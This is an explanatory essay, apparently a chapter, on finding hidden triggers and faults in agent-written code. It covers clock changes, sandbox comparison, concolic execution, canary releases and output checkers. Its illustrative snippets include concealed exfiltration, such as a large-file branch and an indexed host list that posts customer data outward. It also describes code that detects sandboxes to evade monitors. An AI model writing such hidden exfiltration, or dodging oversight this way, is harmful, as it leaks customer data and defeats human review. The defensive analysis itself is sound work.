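The version of the renewal program that takes today's date from the clock passes every test until 29 February 2028. If the monitor sets the sandbox's clock to that date, the program crashes on the first customer. The date is easy to change, and so are most of the other conditions that a test normally keeps fixed.

### Changing one thing at a time

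The monitor first runs the program in the ordinary way and keeps the trace. It then repeats the run with a single change and compares the two traces. For the faults in the earlier examples, these changes would be enough:

| Change to the ordinary run | What it would expose |
|---|---|
| Set the clock to 29 February 2028 | The leap-day crash |
| Early on 1 March 2028 in Sydney, switch the machine to UTC | The same crash, on a day when a local test passes |
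| Have the imitation service refuse requests after the first thousand | Customers that the program silently drops |
| Keep the same machine for 150 runs | Duplicated output, or harm that starts after the hundredth run |
| Supply 60,000 invented customers | The copy of the file sent to an outsider |

Some differences are expected. If the clock moves forward a day, the renewal dates of new customers should move too. The side effects should stay the same, so a new connection is suspicious even when half the output has legitimately changed. Shifting the clock also causes false alarms. If the date is several years ahead, for example, security certificates will have expired and the program's encrypted connections may fail.

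With five things to vary and ten values for each, changing one at a time takes 46 runs, while testing every combination takes 100,000. Changing one at a time misses any behaviour that needs two unusual values at once, such as a large file on a particular date. Dates are easy to cover more thoroughly. One run for each day of the next five years is about 1,800 runs, which take an hour at two seconds each.

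### Comparing a sandbox with an ordinary machine

If code behaves well because it detects the sandbox, the monitor can run it elsewhere and look for a difference. But two runs of a harmless program often differ too.

Balzarotti, Cova and colleagues (2010), in *Efficient Detection of Split Personalities in Malware*, used recording and replay to find programs that behave differently under analysis. They ran each program on a reference machine and logged its system calls and every result the operating system returned. They then ran the program in the analysis system and replayed the logged results, so that it read the same time, settings and network data in both places. If its system calls still differed, it had probably detected the analysis system from something about the processor or the timing.

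The researchers modified the source code of SDBot, a known piece of malware, to make six versions, each with a different check for a virtual machine. The method detected all six, as well as all ten real samples that came wrapped in software known to recognise the analysis system or fail in it. Ten other samples had no such checks. Five of them still behaved differently in the two systems without replay, which would have raised false alarms, but all ten matched once the researchers turned it on.

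Recording and replaying added only about 1% to the running time. But the method misses a program that delays its check until after the analysis ends, and it may miss one that recognises both machines as test machines. Replay also gives the program the same date twice, so it can't expose the leap-day crash. To find that crash, the monitor has to change the clock in separate runs.

A company can use a close copy of its production server as the reference machine. This should expose code that behaves well only when it detects a sandbox. Code that waits for a sign of production that the copy lacks, such as the real customer database, will behave well on both machines, so the traces will match.

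### Reading the code that never ran

After all these runs, a coverage tool can list the lines that none of them executed. If every test file was small, the list for the leaking renewal program might look like this:

```
renewals.py: 34 lines, never executed: 23, 24

22    if len(customers) > 50_000:
23        body = json.dumps(customers, default=str)
24        requests.post(ARCHIVE_URL, data=body)
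```

For each line on the list, the agent or a programmer has to supply a test that runs it, explain why no test can, or delete it. An agent might say that these two lines back up large files. Whoever asked for the program can then say whether they wanted a backup.

This combines running and reading code well, because the tests show the reader where to look. A reader who might skim past two lines in a long program will probably read them carefully when they are the only two on the list.

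The list can be long, though, because error handling often goes unexecuted for innocent reasons and a program usually runs only a small part of each library it imports. A company could restrict the list to the agent's own code, but would then miss harmful branches in the packages that code uses. It should also measure coverage on the exact files it will release, since these can differ from the source code, as they did with XZ.

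An empty list doesn't prove much either. The original leap-year line ran in every test and still failed for one date. Deliberate conditions can avoid the list too:

```python
requests.post(HOSTS[len(customers) > 50_000], data=summary)
```

Python treats a false comparison as 0 and a true one as 1, so this line sends the summary to the first address for a small file and to the second for a large one. Every test executes the line, and it contains no branch for the tool to report. Someone reading the code might still ask why the program needs two addresses.

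### Solving for the condition

A tool can also work out which input would make a branch run. Suppose an agent's program contains these three lines:

```python
code = 3 * reference + 7
if code == 1_000_000:
    send(customers)
```

The tool starts with an ordinary run in which the reference number is 20. The code is then 67, and the program skips the last line. During the run, the tool also treats the reference number as an unknown, *r*, and records the condition that made the program skip the line, 3*r* + 7 ≠ 1,000,000. It negates this condition to get 3*r* + 7 = 1,000,000 and passes it to a solver, a program that finds values satisfying a set of conditions. The solver returns 333,331. When the tool runs the program again with that number, the program sends the file.

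This took two runs, whereas random testing could take hundreds of thousands of years to find one 64-bit number. Running a program on unknowns such as *r* is called symbolic execution, and combining it with ordinary runs on concrete values, as here, is called concolic execution. When a run passes several branches, the tool keeps the constraints from earlier branches, negates the constraint from a later one and solves them together. A tool that follows the calculation into Python's date library could in principle find 29 February by negating the library's check that the day is valid.

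#### What it found in malware

In *Exploring Multiple Execution Paths for Malware Analysis*, Moser, Kruegel and Kirda (2007) applied a version of this to 308 real malware samples. Their system tracked what each program read from the clock, files, the network and similar sources. When such a value decided a branch, the system took a snapshot of the program and let it continue. Later the system restored the snapshot, changed the value and ran the other branch.

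Of the 308 samples, 172 made decisions based on the tracked values. In 151 of those, exploring the other branches increased the amount of code that ran by more than 10%. The largest increase was over 3,400%, for a worm that did its damage only if its own file name contained "upu.exe". One virus just copied itself on its first run and turned harmful only once it found that copy, so a sandbox that began each run from a clean snapshot would have recorded only the installation.

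The system gave each sample 100 seconds, and 42% still had unexplored paths when the time ran out, so more time would have revealed more code. But some of the extra code was only error handling, and a person still had to judge whether the rest was harmful.

In *Automatically Identifying Trigger-based Behavior in Malware*, Brumley, Hartwig and colleagues (2008) tested a similar tool, MineSweeper, on four real programs. The user names a source of information, such as the clock, and MineSweeper searches for values from it that trigger new behaviour.

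| Program | What it waited for | Time to analyse |
|---|---|---|
| NetSky, an email worm | Certain hours of one date | 9 minutes |
| MyDoom, an email worm | Particular dates | 28 minutes |
| Perfect Keylogger | A word in a window's title | 2 minutes |
| TFN, an attack tool | Commands from the network | 21 minutes |

NetSky attacked only between 6 and 9 a.m. on 26 February 2004. A tester who tried every date but always set the clock to noon would have missed the attack. MineSweeper found the hours by solving for the condition that triggers it.

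MineSweeper recovered all the known triggers in the four samples. Four samples are too few to estimate how often the method would succeed on others, and a person had to help with the keylogger by supplying a summary of a standard text-search function. The analysis was quick partly because at most about one in 20,000 instructions depended on the chosen source, so MineSweeper could run the rest normally and use slow symbolic reasoning only on those few.

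### Looking for suspicious conditions

Finding the condition may be enough, without working out how to meet it. *TriggerScope* (Fratantonio, Bianchi and colleagues, 2016) describes a static tool that looks for narrow checks in Android apps, such as comparing the date, the phone's location or the text of a message with a fixed value. The tool reports a check only if the check controls something sensitive, such as network access.

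TriggerScope detected all 14 malicious apps in its test set, including 11 that a government contractor had designed to be hard to detect. TriggerScope also flagged 35 of more than 9,300 apps from Google's app store (0.38%). Most of the conditions it flagged had harmless purposes, such as enforcing an expiry date or greeting visitors to a Japanese railway station. But two apps contained previously unknown backdoors. One was supposed to let owners lock their phones remotely, but a long fixed message would unlock any phone that used it.

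A much larger test did not reproduce TriggerScope's low false-alarm rate. The tool's code isn't public, so Samhi and Bartel (2021), in *On The (In)Effectiveness of Static Logic Bomb Detection for Android Apps*, wrote their own version from the published description. They ran it on 508,122 apps and reported a false-alarm rate of more than 17%. They could get close to TriggerScope's rate only by using aggressive filters or a much shorter list of sensitive operations. In one case they had to remove 90% of the list, so the tool would have missed many real triggers.

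A company whose agents write 500 programs a day would get about two false alarms a day at the lower rate and 85 at the higher. Neither rate comes from agent-written code, but 85 programs a day would be a lot for reviewers to check unless each one is short. Samhi and Bartel suggest using the method to help an analyst locate malicious code, which seems more realistic than using it as the only check.

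A search for narrow comparisons also finds nothing in the original leap-year program, because the agent never wrote a comparison with 29 February. The condition comes from how Python's date library works.

### Too many paths and too many outside services

Solving becomes much harder as programs grow, because each independent branch can double the number of possible paths. University of Maryland's *Concolic Execution* (2026), a set of course slides, gives a function with three separate if-statements, which has eight paths. Forty branches can produce about a trillion paths, and a tool that explored a thousand a second would need 35 years to cover them. Loops make this worse. If a program loops through a file of twenty customers and treats each in one of two ways, it has over a million possible paths.

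Tools therefore have to prioritise some paths over others. MineSweeper explores untried branches before repeating the body of a loop. This is a sensible way to look for hidden behaviour, but it can miss code that runs only after many repetitions.

The solver also can't follow a calculation into the databases and other services that a program calls, so somebody has to write a model of what each service might return. A model that returns one fixed answer hides most of the program's behaviour, while one that allows any answer produces failures that could never happen with the real service.

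Writing these models by hand for every project is slow, and language models can now do much of the work. *Bug Finding with Agentic Symbolic Execution* (Granberry, Ahrendt and colleagues, 2026) paired an AI agent with CrossHair, a concolic tool for Python, and tested the combination on 11 web applications with over a million lines of code. The agent reads the project to find the rules its database enforces and writes a model that respects them. It also writes a contract for each function, stating what the function accepts and what should be true after it runs. CrossHair then looks for inputs that break the contracts.

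On its own, CrossHair could execute only 4.5% of the 5,406 functions with contracts, but with the agent's model of the database it could execute 81%. Most of the violations it reported were false alarms caused by the approximate model, so a second agent reviewed them and the system tried to reproduce each apparent bug in the unmodified application. The system confirmed 221 bugs that CrossHair had found, mostly crashes on odd but permitted inputs, such as an empty string or a missing field. The first agent had noticed another 829 while writing the contracts.

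Granberry and colleagues also had the same language model read the code without the solver. It found 1,824 bugs, more than the combined system's 1,050, but missed 312 of those 1,050, including a third of the ones CrossHair had found. Solving was therefore more useful as an addition to reading than as a replacement for it. However, the bugs were ordinary mistakes, and the study didn't test whether the system could find conditions that someone had deliberately hidden. CrossHair explored only 3.6% of the functions exhaustively, so it could have missed such conditions in the rest.

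A language model can also do the symbolic reasoning itself. In *Agentic Concolic Execution*, Luo, Zhao and colleagues (2026) let agents summarise the constraints in ordinary language and reason about them, so nobody has to model each outside service by hand. On 12 real programs, the paper reports code coverage 115% to 233% higher than conventional tools such as KLEE. The project's web page, *ConcoLLMic*, gives an average cost of about $0.21 per test case. The coverage gain is large, but it is an average over ordinary code, and a hidden trigger may be a single branch that the tests still don't reach.

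It matters that these systems run the program to check the model's suggestions. *Can Large Language Models Simulate Symbolic Execution Output Like KLEE?* (2025) asked GPT-4o to predict KLEE's results for 20 programs without running the tool, and it was right only about 20% of the time. Current models would probably do better. Even so, running the program can expose a wrong guess about an input, whereas a wrong claim that no input can reach a branch might go unnoticed. *Symbolic Execution in Practice* (2025), a survey, also suggests using language models to choose paths and stand in for outside services, but names their probabilistic nature as a main concern.

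### Conditions that can't practically be solved

Some calculations are easy to perform but impractical to reverse. Ordinary software uses them, for instance, to check a password without storing it. If a branch depends on the result of such a calculation, the solver can confirm that a given input reaches the branch but has no practical way to find such an input. More computing time or a better language model doesn't help much.

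The monitor can still find out what the code behind the branch does. Brumley and colleagues suggest continuing along the path as if the condition were true, much as PyFEX does with Python packages. The results must be interpreted carefully, because the program may crash or do something impossible in a normal run when its values don't match the path it is on. But if a forced run tries to send out the customer file, the monitor has the evidence it needs, even if it never finds an input that triggers the behaviour.

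Moser and colleagues write that frequent branches their system can't resolve "could be interpreted as malicious", and suggest passing such programs to a person. They were analysing strangers' software, where rejecting every such program would also reject many useful ones. A company can be stricter with code that its own agent wrote for a known purpose. Calculating a renewal date doesn't require a condition that a solver can't resolve and the agent can't explain, so the company can refuse the program and ask for a simpler one.

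Programs that log users in or verify signatures have good reasons to include such conditions. The reviewer can ask the agent to use a standard library function for them and can check what the program does after each outcome. A correct password should open the user's account without also changing how the program calculates renewals.

### Giving the code less to depend on

All these searches are easier if the program has fewer conditions to search. The company can ask the agent to keep the calculation separate from anything that reads the clock, the network or stored files:

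```python
def renew(start):
    return start.replace(year=start.year + 1)

renewal = renew(date.today())
```

The fault is still there, but now only the last line reads the clock. The monitor can give `renew` every date that Python accepts, as in the earlier exhaustive test, without changing the machine's clock. The results from CrossHair also support separating outside calls from the rest of the code, since it could execute very few functions until something stood in for the database, and code that makes no outside calls doesn't need a stand-in.

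The company can also require each program to declare what it uses:

```
read       /work/customers.csv
write      /work/renewals.csv
network    none
clock      today's date, supplied once at the start
```

A reviewer can compare this list with the task before looking at any code. The restrictions should then apply in production as well as in the test. The branch that sends out large files could still run, but the connection would fail and the attempt could alert someone. This would prevent the leak even if nobody had found the condition that triggers it. The rules should also forbid the program from downloading or generating code while running, because nobody can review or test that code before release.

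Hiding the date from a program is harder than denying it access to the network. The latest start date in the customer file roughly reveals today's date, so a program could wait for 2028 without reading the clock. The file's size and content are also hard to hide, since the program must read the file to do its job.

A program can also do harm using only the permissions it needs for its normal job. Fratantonio and colleagues tested their 14 malicious apps with Kirin, an older tool that judges Android apps by the permissions they request, and it missed eight. Their example is a navigation app for soldiers that starts recommending longer routes after a certain date. Both the normal and the harmful behaviour need only the phone's location and a network connection. A renewal program with access to only its two files could likewise start giving some customers the wrong date once one of those files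 shows that 2028 has arrived.

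## What can be checked only while the program is in use?

A tester can set a sandbox's clock to 29 February, but can't easily simulate a million customers making the mistakes that real ones make, or the load on a database at nine on a Monday morning. According to Google's *Canarying Releases*, a chapter on releasing software safely, even a fully automated process can't detect every defect before real traffic reaches the new version.

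Artificial traffic helps, but it leaves out much of the stored state that builds up in real use. It can also be dangerous. Google warns that fake requests to a billing system could charge real customers.

Sometimes the condition is an ordinary one that nobody tried. In *The Structural Engineer's Other Job*, Meiklejohn (2026) describes tests that Claude wrote for his app, which lists live shows. The livestream test looked for a button during the day and never ran while a show was on.

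### A near-copy of production

A company can get closer to real conditions without involving customers. In *Make Every PR Prove Itself*, the cybersecurity company Abnormal AI describes how it does this for more than 200 agent-written pull requests a day. The agent starts the service it changed in a "testbox" with nearly the same settings as production. Requests to any other service go to a shared test copy, so the company doesn't have to duplicate its whole platform for every change.

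Each testbox has its own databases. Abnormal AI copies some of them from an existing test system and fills others with synthetic records, because it doesn't want captured messages left in a sandbox. In one example, an agent added a field showing the delay between sending a message and evaluating it. To test the field, the agent inserted four rows with known times, requested them through the running service and checked every delay.

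The account describes two failures that looked like successes. In one, an agent submitted a screenshot of a blank page as evidence, because the server had reported success and the page title was right. In the other, two components ignored the testbox's settings and connected to the wrong databases without any error. Abnormal AI now records each testbox's actual connections and compares them with the declared ones.

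Agents used over 3,000 testboxes in 30 days. At 200 pull requests a day, that is fewer than one testbox per pull request, so some changes probably shared a testbox or had none. The company doesn't report how many faults the testboxes caught or missed, but it writes that "some behaviors never show up before merge", and it adds a new check whenever such a behavior causes trouble in production.

### From recorded requests to real customers

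After these tests, a company can expose the program to real use in steps:

| Step | What it can reveal | Main risk | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Replay recorded requests | Faults that depend on real data | Leaking private data | Conditions absent from the recording |
| Shadow run: copy live traffic and discard the outputs | Faults under today's load | Repeated side effects, such as a second charge | Customers' reactions to the new program's answers |
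| Release to a small share of users | Faults with real users and services | Harm before anyone notices | Rare faults and the strain of full load |
| Widen the share | Rarer faults and heavier load | Harm to more users | Wrong answers that nobody measures, and later dates |

To do a replay, the company could save a month of sign-ups and run both the old and new renewal programs on them. Because these inputs come from real use, the 3/*n* rule applies better to real customers than it does when the inputs are invented. But sign-ups recorded in March don't include a leap day. The sandbox now also contains real names, which a malicious program could try to steal. Replacing them with invented names reduces that risk, but might remove an unusual surname that would make the program crash.

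A shadow run sends live requests to both the old program and the new one, and discards the new one's replies. Discarding a reply doesn't undo what the program did while preparing it, so a customer could receive two emails or pay twice. The new program therefore needs its own database and stand-ins for services such as payments, which means the shadow run doesn't test it with the real services. Google adds that the two versions can affect each other's measurements. If they share a cache, the old program may already have loaded the data that the new one needs, making the new one look faster than it is.

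The next step is a canary release, in which a small share of users get the new version. In Google's example, the new version fails on 20% of requests but receives only 5% of the traffic, so 1% of all requests fail. That can go unnoticed among ordinary errors, so the company has to measure each version separately. It should also compare them over the same period, since people may use the service differently at weekends.

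CloudKitchens, which processes restaurant orders, used canaries for over 80% of its releases. Dauginis and Chen report in *Deployment Confidence in Era of AI Coding* that the company's system blocked more than 1,100 bad releases in the third quarter of 2025. They say the company tracks false alarms and missed faults, but they don't publish either rate.

A canary release, which sends a small share of traffic to the new version, can still harm customers. Dauginis and Chen calculate that at 1,000 orders a minute, a faulty version with 5% of the traffic could affect 150 customers even if the company withdraws it after three minutes. Rare faults also take a long time to appear. If one order in 10,000 fails, the canary must handle about 30,000 orders for a 95% chance of at least one failure. At 50 orders a minute, that takes ten hours, and one failed order probably wouldn't stop the release.

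A canary can also miss a problem with load. If the new version sends ten times as many queries to a shared database, giving it 5% of the traffic raises the total by only 45%. The database may handle that and then fail at full release. Google therefore recommends increasing the share in stages. The early stages check for clear signs of trouble, such as crashes, and later ones examine subtler measurements once more users have the new version.

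Those measurements are the oracle, and they can be misleading. At CloudKitchens, a canary couldn't show whether someone had deleted part of a service by mistake, because there was nothing left to compare. In other cases, a change to the data format made the new version look healthier than the old one, which couldn't read the new format. The company now also tracks important operations from end to end across its services. Even so, a renewal program that adds 365 days would return its wrong dates quickly and without raising errors, so measurements of speed and failures wouldn't reveal the mistake.

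Widening the release gradually doesn't help if the condition arrives after the rollout, as with the leap-day crash or a time bomb.

### What a rollback can't undo

When the measurements look bad, the company can roll back by returning all traffic to the old version. CloudKitchens originally did this automatically whenever any check failed, but unreliable measurements caused many unnecessary rollbacks. It now rolls back immediately only when one of its most dependable checks fails. Other failed checks alert an engineer, who can order a rollback, and failed experimental checks only produce a log entry.

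Rolling back traffic is quick, but arc42's *Canary deployment* points out that correctness also depends on what the new version has already written to shared data. If the renewal program saved wrong dates, the company can recalculate them from the start dates, if it kept those. It can refund a payment taken by mistake, but it can't unsend an email or take back a customer file that has reached an outsider.

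Giving a new version to only a small share of users doesn't limit how much data it can leak. A program that serves 5% of customers may still be able to read every customer's records. Google notes that its calculation of the harm from a canary release covers only lost availability, not incidents such as data leaks.

For actions that can't be undone, the company has to prevent the harm, because an alert would come too late. The limits on files and connections declared before release can block a leak if they stay in force, but some irreversible actions, such as sending renewal emails, are part of the program's job. The company could hold those emails for a few hours before sending them, limit how many go out at once, or have a person approve large batches. These precautions take time, so they make most sense where a mistake would do serious harm.

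Alerts are more useful for behaviour that is merely unexpected. The monitor can compare the production trace with the traces from testing and report a new file, process or connection. It could also report when the program first runs a line that no test executed, such as one in the branch for files of more than 50,000 rows. Many of these alerts will be about harmless behaviour, since real use triggers error handling that tests missed. The company might therefore log most of them and stop the program only if the new behaviour could do lasting damage.

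### Checking every answer

Permissions and alerts don't show whether an answer is right, but for some tasks a company can check the answer every time the program runs. Blum and Kannan (1989), in *Designing Programs That Check Their Work*, developed the idea of a program checker, which tests whether the program's output is correct for the input it has just received.

UC Davis' *Lecture 10*, a set of course notes, defines a checker by two conditions. If the program is correct on every input, the checker always accepts its output. If the program is wrong on the current input, the checker rejects the output with very high probability. Neither condition covers a faulty program that gets the current answer right.

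Schoolchildren use a simple checker when they confirm that *a* − *b* = *c* by checking that *b* + *c* = *a*. A good checker is quicker than the original calculation. It therefore can't just repeat that calculation, which makes it less likely to repeat the program's mistake.

Sometimes the program has to supply extra information, called a certificate, for a checker to use. In *Program Correctness through Self-Certification*, Namjoshi and Zuck use the example of sorting a list of numbers. A checker can confirm in one pass that the output is in order, but confirming that it contains the same numbers as the input is about as hard as sorting. If the program also reports each number's original position, the checker can confirm this in one more pass. The same checker works for any sorting program, and theirs is short enough that they could prove it correct.

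A certificate could also expose the navigation app that starts recommending longer routes after a certain date. Suppose all the roads are two-way. The app would give each junction a number so that the numbers at the two ends of any road differ by no more than the road's length. Every route between two places must then be at least as long as the difference between their numbers, so if the recommended route is exactly that long, no route is shorter. The checker needs only one pass through the list of roads, and the check works equally well on any date.

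### Freivalds' check of a matrix product

Rūsiņš Freivalds published a well-known check for matrix multiplication in 1977. A matrix is a grid of numbers, and the ordinary way to multiply two *n* by *n* matrices takes *n*³ multiplications. Suppose a program claims that *A* times *B* is *C*. The checker does the following:

1. Choose a random vector *r*, a list of *n* numbers that are each 0 or 1 with equal probability.
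2. Multiply *B* by *r*, then multiply *A* by the result.
3. Multiply *C* by *r*.
4. Reject *C* if the results of steps 2 and 3 differ.

A correct product always passes, because *A*(*Br*) is the same as (*AB*)*r*. Ji, Mascagni and Li (2017), in *Gaussian Variant of Freivalds' Algorithm for Efficient and Reliable Matrix Product Verification*, give an example, for a different method, in which a memory fault swaps the product's two columns:

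```
A = 2 3    B = 1 -6    correct = 5 6    returned = 6 5
    3 4        1  6              7 6               6 7
```

The wrong answer has the same row and column totals as the right one, so comparing totals doesn't reveal the fault. In Freivalds' check, if *r* = (1, 0), then *Br* is (1, 1) and *A*(*Br*) is (5, 7). The returned matrix times *r* is (6, 6), so the checker rejects it. It would also reject the matrix with *r* = (0, 1), but not with (0, 0) or (1, 1), so one round with a random *r* has a 50% chance of catching the fault.

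A wrong product has at most a 50% chance of passing a round. *Human-LLM Deliberation as Interactive Proof* (2026) includes a short proof. Let *D* be the difference between *AB* and *C*. If *C* is wrong, *D* has a nonzero entry in some row *j* and column *k*. If the other numbers in *r* stay the same, changing the *k*th from 0 to 1 changes the *j*th entry of *Dr*, so at most one of the two choices makes that entry zero. The wrong product passes only if every entry of *Dr* is zero, so it passes for at most half of the possible vectors.

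Each round takes three products of a matrix and a vector, or 3*n*² multiplications. For 1,000 by 1,000 matrices, 20 rounds take 60 million multiplications, and the ordinary product takes a billion. Strassen's faster method needs about 280 million, so the check still takes less work. If each round uses a new random vector, a wrong product passes all 20 with probability at most (1/2)²⁰, less than one in a million. The UC Davis notes suggest that efficient code of this kind may be more complicated and so more likely to contain bugs, which makes a simple checker more useful.

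The program mustn't have access to the random vectors until it has returned its answer, or it could return a wrong matrix that passes. Because computers store most fractions approximately, the checker also has to allow small differences, so a small enough error can pass as rounding.

### Hidden conditions and the limits of checkers

If a hidden condition only affects outputs that a checker can test, nobody needs to find the condition. Suppose a program multiplies matrices correctly until 2028 and then starts returning wrong answers. Freivalds' check is run on each answer as the program returns it, and the chance of missing a wrong one is still at most one in a million because the randomness comes from the checker. The same is true if the trigger is a particular server or a large file. When an answer fails the check, the company can withhold it and use a slower, trusted program instead.

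The checker itself must be correct, and the agent must not be able to change it. In *Zero-Trust Formal Methods*, Philipp (2026) had AI agents write checkers for the proofs that solvers produce when they report that a problem has no solution. His environment blocked the agents' ordinary attempts to edit the specifications after review, though he acknowledges that an agent could deliberately disable that protection. He also found faults in three existing proof checkers that could make them accept invalid proofs. A deliberately altered copy of one of his own checkers passed formal verification even though it printed "verified" for every proof it should have rejected. Philipp then extended the verification to cover the step that prints the result.

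Many tasks have no quick check. *Maverick* (2026) points out that Freivalds' method saves no work when the task is to multiply a matrix by a single vector, because checking the answer takes about as much work as calculating it. Other tasks lack a precise definition of a right answer. A checker can confirm that a summary is under 200 words, but not that it includes what the reader needed. Namjoshi and Zuck also list programs that run indefinitely, such as operating systems, as an open problem.

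Checking the output doesn't detect side effects either. Freivalds' check accepts a correct matrix product even if the program also sent both input matrices to an outsider, so the company still needs the limits on connections.
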